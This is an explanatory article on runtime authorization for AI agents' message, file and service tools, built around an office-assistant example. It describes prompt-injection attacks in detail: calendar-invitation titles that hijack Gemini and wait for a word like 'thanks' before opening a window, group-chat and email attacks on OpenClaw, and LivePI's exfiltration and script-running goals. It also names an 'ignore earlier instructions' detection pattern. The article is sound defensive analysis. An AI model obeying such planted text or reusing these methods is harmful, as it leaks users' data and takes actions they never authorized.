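# Authorizing AI agents' tool calls to messages, files and external services

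## What it means to authorize an agent's tool call

An AI agent is a language model connected to software that can take actions, such as sending an email, saving a file or changing a customer's record. The model only produces text, so to act it writes a *tool call*, a structured request to run a named tool with given arguments. The *runtime*, the ordinary software around the model, then executes or refuses the request. Authorizing a tool call means deciding, outside the model and before the call runs, whether to allow it, refuse it or ask a person. This decision is called an *authorization check*. Agents need these checks because they read a lot of text written by strangers, who can word an email or document so that the agent acts for them instead of for its user.

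Suppose an AI office assistant works for one employee. It reads and sends her email, opens and shares files on the company drive, and looks up and edits supplier records in the accounting system. She asks it to find the quarterly report and send it to Alice. This request is an example from *When Tool Outputs Become Commands* (2026), a paper on runtime authorization from the Chinese Academy of Sciences.

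### The tool-call loop

The assistant handles the request in a loop:

1. The runtime sends the model the employee's request together with a list of tools, each with a name, a description and a schema for its arguments.
2. The model answers with a tool call, say `search_files(query="quarterly report")`.
3. The runtime takes the name and the arguments out of that answer and runs the search.
4. The runtime adds the result, a file path, to the conversation and sends the whole conversation back to the model.
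5. The model now has the path in its context, the text from which it produces its next output, and proposes `send_email(to="alice@firm.example", attachment="reports/q3.pdf")`. The loop continues until the model gives a final answer instead of another call.

OpenAI's *Function calling* and Anthropic's *How tool use works*, the two companies' guides for developers, describe essentially this sequence. In Anthropic's words, "the model never runs anything on its own." The natural time to check a call is therefore after the model proposes it and before the runtime executes it, while the call is still only data. The weak point comes after execution, because whatever the tool returns enters the same context as the employee's own words, and the model's next proposal depends on all of it.

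Some tools don't work this way. Anthropic runs web search, web page retrieval and a code sandbox on its own servers, and those operations have usually finished by the time the developer's program receives a response, so a check in the developer's runtime comes too late to stop them. The developer's main decision is whether to enable these tools.

### Identity, credentials and authority

When the email reaches the company's mail server, the server requires a credential, and the runtime presents a valid one. This step is authentication, which is distinct from authorization. *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems*, the 1975 paper by Saltzer and Schroeder that fixed much of the field's vocabulary, defines authenticating as verifying the identity of whoever makes a request, and authorizing as granting a principal (an entity that can hold authority) access to certain information.

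Holding a credential does not establish that a tool call is authorized. A plain API key is a secret string that opens a service to anyone who holds it, so the service cannot tell the intended agent from a hijacked one. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) makes a similar point about tokens with a scope, a permission that limits which operations the holder may perform. A scope such as `email.send` does not specify the task, the recipient or any limit on the content, so it allows an email to a thief as well as one to Alice. Authorizing the call also requires deciding whether it may run with these arguments, for this user and this task.

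Surapani and colleagues identify whose authority is involved by arranging the parties in a *principal hierarchy* of five layers. Layer 0 is the human user, the source of legitimate authority. Layer 1 is the operator, the organization that deploys the agent, sets its policies and supplies its credentials. Layer 2 is the main agent, which interprets the task and selects tools, and Layer 3 contains any sub-agents that do parts of the work for it. Layer 4 consists of the tool endpoints, such as mail servers, file systems and databases. Authority should only narrow as it passes down the layers. The user and the operator can each rule out a call, since an employee may ask for something her company forbids, and a company may run tools that a particular employee has no right to use.

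Layer 4 is awkward because an inbox is both something the agent needs permission to use and a source of text from anyone who knows the address. The check described in the review therefore uses two separate records, one of who passed authority to whom and one of where each piece of content came from.

### Indirect prompt injection and the confused deputy

In early prompt injection, users typed text into a chatbot to override the developer's instructions. *Not what you've signed up for* (Greshake, Endres and colleagues, 2023) introduced the term *indirect prompt injection* for instructions that a third party plants in material the model is likely to retrieve. The paper demonstrated the attack against Bing's GPT-4 chat, code-completion engines and test applications built for the study. An attacker can deliver the text passively, by leaving it on a web page or in a code repository, or actively,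 by emailing it to someone whose assistant reads the mail. The paper also sketched an assistant that reads such an email, collects personal data and sends it out, and an email worm that copies its own instructions into every message the assistant writes.

By October 2026, the security company Barracuda had found phishing emails with hidden instructions meant to manipulate AI assistants as well as the people who use them, according to *Attackers Hide AI Prompt Injections Inside Phishing Emails* (Mascellino, 2026).

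Prompt injection works because a language model has no separate input for data that it will never treat as instructions. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a post by David C for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre, compares it with the older SQL injection attack, in which someone enters database commands into a web form. Developers solved that problem with parameterized queries, which pass the visitor's input separately so that the database engine never interprets it as a command. A language model predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from all the text so far, and any distinction it makes between instructions and data is at best a tendency learned in training. David C concludes that the model is an "inherently confusable deputy."

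The term "confused deputy" comes from Hardy's *The Confused Deputy*, which describes an incident at the timesharing company Tymshare. A compiler there had permission to write in its home directory, where it kept a file of usage statistics. The company's billing records were in the same directory. The compiler also let users name a file to receive debugging output, and one user named the billing file. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission to write in that directory, and the billing data was lost. Hardy wrote that the compiler "serves two masters": it had authority from its own installation and from the user, but no way to state which one a given request relied on.

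Surapani and colleagues describe a case in which a user authorizes an agent to summarize the invoices in an inbox. One message contains text that requests a payment. The agent hands the request to a finance sub-agent without passing on the restriction that the task was read-only. The payment service receives a valid credential and makes the payment. Every identity check succeeds, and the service cannot detect that a stranger's email prompted the request.

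Hardy's remedy was the *capability*, a reference that names a file and carries the right to use it, so the user hands over the authority along with the name. This worked because the compiler's code had one fixed place for statistics and another for debugging output. A model handles the user's request and the stranger's text in one probabilistic process, so David C argues that this flaw, unlike the classical one, can only be mitigated, not cured.

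That was in December 2025, and models have improved since. According to The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt injection*, attacks on Anthropic's Claude Opus 5 failed in all 129 of the company's browser scenarios. In a broader test by the security firm Gray Swan, attackers succeeded 2.0 percent of the time after 15 attempts, down from 5.5 percent for the previous model. This removes much of the everyday risk, but tool calls still need a check because attackers can write to as many inboxes as they choose, and a stolen payment does the same damage however rare such thefts are.

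### Least privilege and complete mediation

*Least privilege* is one of two principles from Saltzer and Schroeder that underlie nearly everything engineers now build to authorize tool calls. It holds that every program and every user should work with "the least set of privileges necessary to complete the job." It mainly limits the damage from an accident or error. An assistant that summarizes invoices needs to read mail, but if it can't make payments, a planted payment request will fail even if the model tries to follow it.

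The principle of *complete mediation* is that "every access to every object must be checked for authority." For an agent, this means checking each tool call, whereas many products ask only once, when the user connects her account. According to the original text, designers should therefore be skeptical of any scheme that saves time by remembering an earlier decision, because authority may have changed since. The system also needs a foolproof way to identify the source of every request. This is hard with agents because the runtime can detect that a call came from the model, but not whether the employee's words or a line in an attachment prompted it.

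Under a companion principle, *fail-safe defaults*, the system refuses any access that nobody has allowed. This makes mistakes easier to notice, because somebody complains when a legitimate call is missing from the list of allowed calls and gets blocked, whereas a call mistakenly left off a list of forbidden calls goes through and may go unnoticed.

### When a call is a violation

*When Tool Outputs Become Commands* turns the problem into a definition. Let $U$ be the user's request and let $c_t = (\tau_t, \theta_t)$ be the call that the model proposes at step $t$, where $\tau_t$ is the tool and $\theta_t$ its arguments. Let $\mathcal{X}_{<t}$ stand for the execution so far, the request together with the earlier calls and their results. $\text{Permitted}_U(c_t \mid \mathcal{X}_{<t})$ is true if the request, together with the legitimate work already done on it, gives the call authority to run.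 Then

$$\text{Violation}_t \triangleq \text{Execute}(c_t) \land \neg\,\text{Permitted}_U(c_t \mid \mathcal{X}_{<t})$$

A violation occurs when a call runs and the user's request did not permit it. The second formula concerns outside text. If $O_i$ is an earlier tool result, then

$$\text{Induced}(c_t, O_i) \not\Rightarrow \text{Permitted}_U(c_t \mid \mathcal{X}_{<t})$$

The fact that an email or a document led the model to propose a call never makes that call permitted.

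Under this definition, an attacker who completely fools the model still achieves nothing if the runtime refuses the resulting call. A violation can also occur without an attacker. For example, if the model picks the wrong Alice from the address book and the email goes out, the first formula is satisfied.

A call can be authorized even if outside information influenced it. The employee never typed `reports/q3.pdf`; the path came from a search result, and the assistant needed it to do its job. The paper calls this *runtime instantiation*, in which outside information fills in a detail of something the user already asked for. Suppose the search result also contains an instruction to send a copy to an outside address. Following that instruction would be *authority expansion*, because it adds a recipient the user never named. A check that blocked every call containing any trace of outside text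 would stop both calls and make the assistant useless.

The definition derives authority from the user's request, so the operator's prohibitions have to be added as a separate condition. It excludes the case where a user tells her assistant to do whatever an email instructs, because she has handed the decision to the email's author. The paper also counts an attack as successful only if it produces an external effect, while Surapani and colleagues treat reads as subject to authorization too. Applying authorization to reads is safer for the office assistant, since a read can put both secrets and planted instructions into the context.

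The larger difficulty is that no program can look up the value of $\text{Permitted}_U$, because it depends on what a person meant by a sentence. Every real check is therefore an approximation that can let a violation through or refuse legitimate work. This includes SARA, the mechanism that the paper builds on its definition.

### Why an instruction in the system prompt is not a check

The easiest way to approximate authorization is to put a rule such as "never email company files to outside addresses" in the system prompt, the text that an operator places before every conversation. *From Alignment to Access Control* (2026) calls this a "Pretty Please" request. The rule is added to the context as more text, so it depends on the model following it, and the model is the component that an attacker is trying to influence.

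Quarkslab, a security company, built a small medical assistant to show the difference. With a loose system prompt, a logged-in patient could get another patient's records by asking for them. A stricter prompt, which limited the assistant to the current patient, blocked the direct request but failed when the researchers gave the assistant a web page with an instruction hidden in a comment. They then went back to the loose prompt and changed the tool's code to compare the requested patient number with the logged-in user's, and the attack failed. The demonstration used a small model from 2024, and a current model might well have resisted the hidden comment, but the check in the code would work with any model.

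Larger tests on newer models gave similar results. *AgentPolicyForge* (2026) tested Claude Sonnet 5 in what it calls threat episodes, with and without the applicable policy in the prompt. Without the policy, the model executed violating calls in over 98 percent of episodes, mostly because it had no way to know the rules. With the policy, it still did so in 14.77 percent of episodes in one set of domains and 13.16 percent in another, and it now wrongly refused about 9 percent of harmless requests. In *Policy-Invisible Violations in LLM-Based Agents* (2026), adding general rules to the prompt reduced violations from 286 to 122 of 300 risky cases. The experimenters had withheld the facts needed to apply those rules, and models used in offices often lack such facts too. For example, a model can't reliably follow a ban on sharing files with former contractors if it can't find out who has left.

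These failures are also easy to miss. *Reason Less, Verify More* (2026) describes how a tool that enforces no rules of its own executes any well-formed call, so a customer-service agent can cancel a non-refundable booking and the transcript will show no error.

The decision therefore has to be made outside the model, but it matters what makes it. When *AgentPolicyForge* used other language models as external guards without special training, violations got through at rates of 10.47 to 16.64 percent, about the same as with the prompt alone. A guard trained for the task lowered the rate to roughly 8 percent. Ordinary code does better when the rule can be stated exactly. AWS's *AGENTSEC02-BP01 Implement tool authorization*, guidance for companies that build agents on Amazon's cloud, calls for a deterministic check of this kind before the tool executes, however the agent arrived at the call. In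 Anthropic's coding agent, Claude Code, the software likewise enforces the permission rules, and the prompt only shapes what the model attempts. The prompt is still worth writing because it can reduce the number of bad calls the check has to catch.

### Message, file and service tools

The details a rule can specify exactly depend on the tool. Anthropic's guide gives three examples of actions with side effects (sending an email, writing a file and updating a record), which correspond to three families of tools. *Message tools* read or send communication between people, such as email, chat and calendar invitations. *File tools* read, write, move, delete or share files on a computer or cloud drive. *Service tools* read or change records in an outside system, such as a database, ticket tracker, code host or payment provider.

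Each family of tools lets an agent both take actions and read text that outsiders wrote. The email tool that sends the report to Alice also brings in messages from strangers. The company drive holds documents that suppliers wrote, and a supplier's record in the accounting system may include a notes field that the supplier filled in. Instructions that arrive through one family can affect what the agent does with another. For example, an instruction in an attached invoice could lead the agent to change the bank details in the supplier's record, and a line in that record could lead it to send email from the employee's account.

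## Listing what each tool reads and what its arguments control

The first job in setting up authorization is to write an inventory of the agent's tools. Nobody can write a sensible rule for an argument without knowing what it controls, and a tool's name often gives little away. The inventory has one row per tool and records four things:

- who can write the text that the tool returns
- what effect a call has outside the conversation
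- whether anyone can undo that effect
- what role each argument plays

The entry for who can write the text a tool reads should name people. An entry such as "the company drive" names only a storage location and omits the fact that suppliers upload files there. For an inbox, the entry should be "anyone who knows the address". Read-only tools need this entry too, because a planted instruction stays in the agent's context after the tool reads it.

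Tool makers sometimes supply part of this information. Under MCP (the Model Context Protocol), an open standard through which agents discover and call tools offered by servers, a server can attach four yes-or-no labels to a tool: whether it only reads, whether its changes are destructive, whether repeating a call with the same arguments is safe, and whether it deals with outside parties. A tool with no labels counts as the worst case on all four, which is also a good default for any blank cell in the inventory. The standard's maintainers stress that the labels are only hints (Model Context Protocol, 2026). A server can label a tool read-only and delete files anyway, so an operator can copy the labels from its own servers but has to work out the entries for a stranger's server itself. The labels also describe only the tool as a whole, not its arguments.

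### The six argument roles

Knowing that `send_email` sends email doesn't help distinguish a good call from a bad one. *The Granularity Mismatch in Agent Security* (Fan, Li and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to summarize a web page and email the summary to her boss. The page should determine the email's body but must not determine its recipient. A rule that treats the call as one unit either blocks the legitimate email or lets the page change the recipient. The paper's runtime monitor, PACT, therefore gives every argument one of six roles, and it also tracks where each value came from.

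| Role | What the argument does | Message tool | File tool | Service tool |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Target | Decides where data or an effect goes | Recipient of an email | Path of the file to write | Account that receives a payment |
| Command | Supplies something for a program to execute | Mailbox rule that forwards matching mail | Shell command that renames files | Database statement that changes records |
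| Credential | Supplies a secret | Mailbox password | Password of an encrypted document | API key |
| Content | Carries what the call sends or stores | Message body | Text to save | Comment on a support ticket |
| Selector | Picks an existing object | ID of the message to delete | ID of the file to share | Customer number |
| Control | Changes how the call behaves | Whether to notify meeting guests | Whether to overwrite an existing file | Whether a payment recurs |

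Targets, commands and credentials are *authority-bearing arguments* because they determine whom or what a call reaches or what it executes. A *content argument* carries only the material. Selectors and controls can be either kind, depending on the tool. A selector that picks which email to read does little damage by itself, but one that picks an attachment determines which file leaves the company.

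An argument's name doesn't reliably show its role. In a mailbox tool, `query` holds harmless search words, but in a database tool it may hold a statement that deletes every record. Fan and colleagues list `path`, `filter` and `id` as ambiguous in the same way. Their software drafts the roles from a tool's name, argument names and description, and it got 87.1 percent of them right on 20 real MCP tools.

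Labeling a target as content is a much more serious mistake than labeling content as a target. When the researchers deliberately labeled every target as content, the share of attacks that PACT stopped fell from 100 to 40 percent. When they labeled all content as a target, PACT still stopped every attack but let only 40 percent of the legitimate work through. Whoever fills in the table should therefore pick the stricter role when in doubt and loosen it when somebody complains. In a seven-day trial, the researchers needed only 75 minutes to set up the requirements for 15 tools.

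### The office assistant's inventory

From here on, we use the office assistant from the previous section as the example. Its inventory below has one reading tool and one writing tool from each family. The arguments loosely follow those in AgentDojo, a public test set of simulated office, chat, banking and travel tasks with planted attacks. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) includes AgentDojo's tool definitions.

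| Tool | Who can write what it returns | Effect | Can she undo it? | Argument roles |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| `read_email(query)` | Anyone who knows her address | None outside the conversation | Nothing to undo | `query`: selector |
| `send_email(to, cc, bcc, subject, body, attachment)` | The company's mail server | Delivers text and a file | No | `to`, `cc`, `bcc`: target; `subject`, `body`: content; `attachment`: selector |
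| `read_file(path)` | Colleagues, and suppliers who upload contracts and invoices | None outside the conversation | Nothing to undo | `path`: target |
| `share_file(file_id, email, permission, message)` | Whoever wrote the file | Opens the file to another person and emails them | Partly: she can withdraw access, but not the email or any copies | `file_id`: selector; `email`: target; `permission`: control; `message`: content |
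| `get_supplier(name)` | Accounting staff, and the supplier for the notes field | None outside the conversation | Nothing to undo | `name`: selector |
| `send_payment(recipient, amount, subject, date)` | The accounting system | Moves money | Rarely, once the bank has sent it | `recipient`: target; `amount`, `date`: control; `subject`: content |

Some of these entries are judgment calls. `path` in `read_file` looks like a selector, but Fan and colleagues treat paths in file operations as targets, which is stricter. An amount of money fits none of the six roles well. The table classes it as control because it changes how much the call does, but a payment tool needs a separate limit on the amount whichever role it is assigned.

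`share_file` is a writing tool that also reads. In AgentDojo's definitions, the equivalent tool returns the whole file record, including the document's text. An ordinary runtime would add that text to the context, so a call that only changes permissions could bring in a planted instruction.

No argument in the table is a credential. This is a good sign, because it means the runtime attaches passwords and tokens itself and the model never handles them. No argument is a command either, which makes the assistant much easier to check than an agent with a shell.

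Suppose the employee writes, "pay the invoice in my contracts folder and mail the receipt to my manager." The assistant uses `read_file` to list the folder and open the invoice, then looks up the supplier with `get_supplier`. It calls `send_payment`, which returns the receipt's location on the drive, and attaches the receipt to an email. The request uses four of the six tools. It doesn't need `read_email` or `share_file`, but an attacker could hide an instruction in the invoice to call either one.

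The folder is the only value the employee typed that the authority-bearing arguments need. Her manager's address has to come from a directory, and the account number and amount are in an invoice that a supplier wrote. *PEAR* (2025), a benchmark for agents that separate planning from execution, reprints a similar task from AgentDojo. The user asks the agent to pay the bill in a named text file, which supplies both the payee and the amount. The agent passes if it sends 98.70 to the right account.

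A rule that a payment's target must never come from outside text would therefore block an honest request, and with no rule at all the assistant would pay any account that a forged invoice named. The inventory doesn't resolve this tradeoff, but it does show that the supplier's record also holds an account number, which can be compared with the one on the invoice. This comparison only helps if the supplier can't edit that field, so where different people can write different parts of a record, the inventory should list the fields separately.

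### Sorting tools by effect

Filling in the effect column from the name of a tool or its product can miss effects, most often when the tool sends messages as a side effect. When a program shares a Google Drive file with someone, Google emails that person by default, and the program can add its own text to the email through the `emailMessage` argument. According to Google's reference page for this call, *Method: permissions.create*, the call requires only a Drive scope. If an agent has that scope, withholding the scope for sending mail won't stop it from emailing strangers.

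The same call has a control argument, `sendNotificationEmail`, that turns the notification off, except when the file changes owner. A runtime could set this argument to "off" and keep the model from changing it. The call would still give the other person access to the file but would no longer deliver a note to them.

Calendar tools have the same side effect. When a program creates an event through Microsoft's Graph interface, the server sends invitations to all the attendees. Google Calendar has an argument that controls which guests are notified, but Google's *Events: insert* warns that some emails may go out even when it is set to none. Google's *Create events* explains that the event also appears on the attendees' own calendars, so an attacker who controls the description and the guest list can deliver stolen text without any email. The inventory therefore treats adding a guest to a meeting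 as sending a message, and `participants` as a target like `to`.

A shell is the extreme case because this one tool can have every effect in the table. *I hacked my own computer using OpenClaw and it was terrifyingly easy* (2026), from the technology site Android Authority, describes a test of OpenClaw, an agent that connects a language model to a person's messaging accounts, files and online services. The tester scheduled a task that summarized unread email every five minutes, then sent the account an email from an unknown address asking for bank details. The agent used shell commands to list the documents folder, find a fake bank statement and mail it back, although the tester had never told it how to send a reply.

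The model was a small, 8-billion-parameter version of Qwen3, and the newer models in the same test were more cautious, so the episode is poor evidence of how often a current model would fall for such an email. It is better evidence of what an inventory can miss, since a row that lists only a shell tool and an argument called `command` doesn't show the recipient or path inside the command string. An operator can replace the shell with narrow tools or give each permitted command its own row.

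### How much the channel matters: the LivePI test

The column for who can write a tool's output matters more if planted text works better from some sources than from others. Zhao, Bhaskar and Dobriban (2026) measured this in *LivePI* on a live installation of OpenClaw. They ran it on a rented server and gave it a web browser, a folder of invented personal files, a cryptocurrency wallet with a small balance, and test accounts on Gmail, WhatsApp, Telegram and Slack. Many earlier tests simulated the email and websites, but here an attack could send a real email or move real money.

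The attacks had five goals: finding wallet files and mailing them out, switching off the firewall and automatic updates, downloading and running a script, mailing a summary of the inbox to an outsider, and transferring cryptocurrency. The researchers delivered them through seven channels, for 169 cases in all:

- Three group chats, on WhatsApp, Telegram and Slack, had one direct request per goal, which makes 15 cases.
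- Email, a local document and a public web post (on GitHub's Gist service) had ten wordings per goal, which makes 150 cases. Some wordings forged a trail of approvals, and others put the attack at the end of an ordinary checklist.
- Links to a malicious code repository accounted for the remaining 4 cases.

An attack counted as successful only if the planted material influenced the agent and the agent achieved the attacker's goal. A language model judged the records of each run, and the researchers also checked the outgoing mail, transactions and security settings. They ran every case with five models.

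| Channel | Cases per model | Claude Opus 4.6 | Kimi K2.5 | GPT-5.3-Codex | GLM-5 | Gemini 3.1 Pro |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Group chat | 15 | 100% | 100% | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| Email | 50 | 2% | 6% | 20% | 6% | 12% |
| Local document | 50 | 0% | 12% | 34% | 50% | 30% |
| Repository link | 4 | 50% | 100% | 100% | 100% | 100% |
| Public web post | 50 | 0% | 0% | 0% | 0% | 20% |
| All cases | 169 | 10.7% | 16.6% | 27.2% | 27.8% | 29.6% |

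Every group-chat attack worked on all five models, each from a different company. A stranger in the group mentioned the agent and told it what to do, without using any tricks. Results this uniform are rare across models from different companies, so the researchers looked for a cause in the software around the models.

They found it in how OpenClaw labels text. A runtime gives the model each piece of a conversation under a label, usually called a role (unrelated to the argument roles above), such as user or tool result. OpenClaw labeled tool output as tool results, but it gave messages from group members the same user role as its owner's requests. The model therefore couldn't tell from the role whether a message came from a stranger or the owner. By default, OpenClaw also let any member of a group address the agent, even from an account that had never paired with it and couldn't message it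 privately. Rules about which senders can instruct the agent would address this, and they belong with the other limits on message tools.

The risk from email depends on how it reaches the agent. In LivePI, the agent fetched its mail with a tool, so the text arrived as a tool result. OpenClaw can also receive mail through a Gmail hook, which passes new messages to the agent as they arrive. In *BrokenClaw Part 1*, the security researcher veganmosfet (2026) showed that a single email sent through the hook could run an attacker's code, and asked the developers to move email text from the user role to the tool role. An inbox that reaches the agent both ways therefore needs two rows in the inventory, each noting the role assigned to the text.

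Operators have to check this for each runtime. Imperva's *WP Compromise OpenClaw with Prompt Injections in Message Objects* describes a related flaw, in which hidden instructions in message data entered the authenticated user's context. The developers fixed it in version 2026.4.23, but LivePI used an earlier version, 2026.3.24. Imperva notes that no standard governs how a runtime turns chat messages into text for a model, so a different agent, or an update to the same one, may behave differently.

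The other channels are harder to compare because the user's request also differed. For the local document, the user asked the agent to complete the items on a to-do list in order, and the attack was one of the items. GLM-5 carried out half of these attacks, but in a sense the user had asked it to. For email, the user asked the agent only to check the five latest messages and reply. The document figures therefore partly measure how literally a model takes a broad request, and they don't show that files are more dangerous than email.

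Unlike the other attacks, the repository attacks didn't require the model to read or follow an instruction, because the malicious package ran its code as soon as the agent imported it. Four cases are too few for a reliable rate, but they show that the package name in an installation tool is a command, even though it looks like a selector, because it decides what code runs.

### What a better model changed

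Claude Opus 4.6 had the best overall result, with 18 successful attacks out of 169. Of these, 15 came through group chat, 2 through repository links and 1 through email. Group chat made up about 9 percent of the cases but 83 percent of the successful attacks.

The overall rates understate the difference between the models. Gemini 3.1 Pro's total of 29.6 percent is just under three times Opus 4.6's. Without group chat, attacks succeeded in 35 of 154 cases against Gemini and 3 of 154 against Opus, a difference of nearly twelve times. Using Opus instead of Gemini stopped almost all the attacks that arrived as tool results but none that arrived as the user's words. An operator already using Opus 4.6 therefore had more to gain from changing how the runtime labeled chat messages than from any further improvement in the model.

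### The defended run

Zhao and colleagues then added a two-layer defense and repeated the attacks on GPT-5.3-Codex, which had failed in 46 of the 169 cases. One layer searches the text for suspicious patterns, such as requests to ignore earlier instructions, before the model reads it. The other checks whether each tool call is authorized. When several rules apply to a call, it uses the strictest decision.

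The check uses much the same information as the inventory. Before applying any rule, the software identifies what kind of operation the call performs and which of its arguments hold paths, destinations or secrets. Opening a private key with a file tool then counts as access to secrets, and running a shell command that downloads and runs a script counts as network activity. The researchers added seven rules to the built-in ones, covering wallet files, firewall settings, email, sensitive documents, credentials, sharing with outsiders and system configuration.

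No attack succeeded with the defense in place. The researchers also ran 123 ordinary tasks from PinchBench, a test set for OpenClaw agents, to see how much the defense would interfere with normal use. Of 899 tool calls, the check sent 8 to a person and blocked 1.

The zero is less impressive because the researchers wrote the seven rules knowing what the attacks would attempt. A wallet rule will stop a wallet attack, but the result is little evidence of how the defense would handle a goal that nobody had anticipated. The researchers tested the defense on one model and didn't repeat the runs to measure chance variation. They also counted attacks as stopped when the check only paused them for review, and those stay harmless only if the person says no.

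The low rate of interruptions also depends on the workload. Zhao and colleagues note that their seven rules didn't cover many of the tools in the ordinary tasks, and that an agent with access to more sensitive resources might trigger more reviews. The email rule typically triggers review when a call reads, searches or sends mail, so the office assistant would probably interrupt its user far more often than once in a hundred calls if it worked in an inbox all day.

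## Setting limits on message tools

Reading and sending messages carry different risks, so they need separate rules. The runtime has to determine whose words count as instructions when the assistant reads messages, and who may receive a message and what may go with it when the assistant sends one.

### Who may give the agent orders

The office assistant is an easy case because it takes orders only from the employee who has logged in. Many agents work through a chat app instead, where anyone who finds the account can write to it. OpenClaw is one of these, and OpenClaw's *Access control and allowlists* describes four policies for direct messages:

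- *Pairing* is the default. An unknown sender receives a code, and the agent ignores that sender until the owner approves it. Codes expire after an hour.
- With *allowlist*, the agent ignores everyone who isn't already on the owner's list and offers no code.
- With *open*, anyone can give orders. The owner has to add a wildcard to the list to turn this on, which makes it hard to do by accident.
- With *disabled*, the agent ignores all direct messages.

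Pairing approves a chat account, not a person, so someone who takes over a paired account can give orders too.

Group chats need more rules, since the owner rarely chooses every member. OpenClaw can limit which groups the agent takes part in and which members it obeys, and it can require a mention of the agent's name. It checks the group and the sender before it looks for a mention. The order matters because a mention doesn't show that the sender had any right to address the agent. The group-chat attacks by Zhao and colleagues succeeded in a setup where any member could address the agent. OpenClaw's *Groups* describes a stricter default, in which the agent blocks group senders until the owner lists them. An open policy is still reasonable in a private room where the owner trusts everyone who can join.

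The list for direct messages has to stay separate from the list for groups. OSV's *CVE-2026-32006* (2026), an entry in a public database of software flaws, describes versions of OpenClaw in which an account paired for direct messages also passed the group check. The flaw has a severity score of only 2.3 out of 10, but it overrode the owner's choice of who could direct the agent in groups. For example, an owner might let a contractor ask the agent private questions without agreeing to let the contractor direct it in a management group.

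These lists control who can start the agent, but they don't limit whose text it sees. If the owner asks for a summary of a chat thread, the model may receive quotes, forwarded messages and history from people who aren't on any list. OpenClaw has a setting that filters out this text, but it is off by default, and turning it on would leave gaps in the summary of any thread that includes outsiders. Direct messages have a similar problem because they all share one session by default, so one person's text can still be in the context when another person gives the agent an instruction. OpenClaw recommends separate sessions when several people can write to the agent.

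### Why the text of an email is only data

An email is weaker evidence of who is speaking than a message from a paired chat account. A sender can forge the "From" line unless the receiving server verifies it, and a genuine message from a colleague may quote or forward a stranger's text. An approval written inside an email, like the forged ones in LivePI, is no more trustworthy than the rest of the email.

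The safest rule is that an email can provide facts for a task but can never start or expand one. If the employee's manager writes, "send me the Q3 figures," the assistant can tell the employee about the request and prepare a draft, but it needs the employee's approval before it sends anything.

Automatic handling of mail is much of what people want from an assistant, and this rule still allows it if the user writes the instructions in advance. OpenAI's *Google app for ChatGPT data controls FAQ* describes tasks that run when a new Gmail message arrives, with optional conditions on the sender or subject. The email determines only when the user's instructions run. A subject condition gives no protection, because a stranger can type any subject. Since nobody may be watching when such a task runs, it should have fewer tools than a task the user supervises. For example, it might be able to save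 drafts but not send them.

### The calendar-invitation attacks on Gemini

"Text" here includes subject lines, event titles, file names and the sender's display name. Nassi, Cohen and Yair (2025), in *Invitation Is All You Need!*, attacked Google's Gemini assistants with little more than titles. One of their attacks opened a window in the victim's home:

1. The attacker sent the victim a calendar invitation. Its title began with markers that imitated the end of the calendar data, followed by instructions to Gemini.
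2. The victim asked Gemini about upcoming events. Gemini's calendar agent fetched the titles and passed them to the central model that plans each task.
3. The planted text told the model to do nothing until the user wrote a word such as "thanks" or "great".
4. The victim thanked Gemini, which then used its Google Home tool to open the window.

The delay bypassed a safeguard that let only Gemini's central model launch specialist agents. The calendar agent couldn't call the home agent itself, but the central model read the calendar agent's output, and the instructions stayed in its context until the next turn.

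The paper lists 14 scenarios, including ones in which Gemini deleted a calendar event, turned on a boiler and joined a Zoom call that streamed video of the user. One attack used two invitations to leak the titles of six meetings. The first made Gemini write the titles into a web address, and the second made it open that address. The attacker needed only the victim's email address and no special skill in attacking models. The researchers ran their experiments on their own accounts with models that are now old, and a current model would probably resist more of these attacks.

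Google Calendar has a setting that automatically adds invitations only from known senders. It would have kept a stranger's invitation title out of the victim's calendar, but not one from a spouse, a colleague or anyone else who had written to the victim before.

Nassi and colleagues recommend a better check, which asks the user to confirm operations that involve outside data. Once the calendar had returned a title written by somebody else, opening a window would have required confirmation, and "thanks" would not have counted. To stop a delayed attack, the runtime has to keep track of the outside text for as long as it remains in the context. If the user's next message ended this tracking, the window would still open. The researchers reported the attacks to Google in February 2025, and Google says it responded with more confirmations, stricter handling of links and classifiers meant to detect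 planted instructions.

### Every argument that decides who receives what

A sent message goes to every address in `to`, `cc` and `bcc`, so the runtime should combine the three fields into one list and check each address. An attacker would prefer `bcc` because the other recipients can't see the addresses in it.

`reply-to` is easier to overlook. It sets the address that receives any reply, so an email sent only to Alice can still direct her response to a stranger. When the assistant replies to an incoming message that has a reply-to address, the mail program sends the reply there instead of to the "From" address, so the author of the incoming message chooses where the assistant's reply goes.

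A tool such as `reply_all(message_id, body)` has no recipient argument. The mail service fills in the recipients from the thread, and anyone in the thread can add an address by copying someone in. The runtime therefore has to look up the full list before it checks the call, and then send to exactly that list in case the thread has changed in the meantime. Mailing lists pose the same problem, since `team@firm.example` may include people outside the company.

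An attachment argument is usually just an ID or a path, so the runtime should look up the file and compare any marking on it, such as "internal", with the recipients. It should do the same for a link in the message body if anyone with the link can open the file.

### Drafting, replying, forwarding and sending

The office assistant's inventory has a single `send_email` tool. Splitting it into separate tools for drafts, replies, forwards and new messages lets the operator set a different rule for each.

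Drafting is the safest action because nobody receives a draft until the employee sends it, although she may not notice a hidden recipient the assistant has filled in. A reply goes to people already in the conversation, which helps when the employee started it, but an attacker can start one too. Forwarding needs the strictest rule because it can send an existing message to anyone, often with its attachments and a long history, so a single wrong address can expose months of correspondence. A new message can also go to anyone, but it contains only what the assistant writes or attaches.

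A sensible starting policy lets the assistant write drafts, lets it reply when every address passes the check, and requires it to ask before forwarding anything outside the company.

### What a Gmail scope can restrict

The operator might hope to enforce this split with the scopes on the assistant's access token. Google's list of Gmail scopes shows how far that can go:

| Scope | What the holder may do |
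|---|---|
| `gmail.metadata` | See labels and headers, but not the body of an email |
| `gmail.readonly` | View messages and settings |
| `gmail.send` | Send email |
| `gmail.compose` | Manage drafts and send email |
| `gmail.modify` | Read, compose and send email, but not delete it permanently without going through the trash |
| `gmail.settings.basic` | Change settings and filters |

Scopes can separate reading from sending. A program that only sends reports can hold `gmail.send`, which gives no access to the inbox. An assistant that only summarizes mail can hold `gmail.readonly`, which doesn't allow sending. Few assistants should have the settings scope, because it lets them create filters that keep acting on new mail after the task is over.

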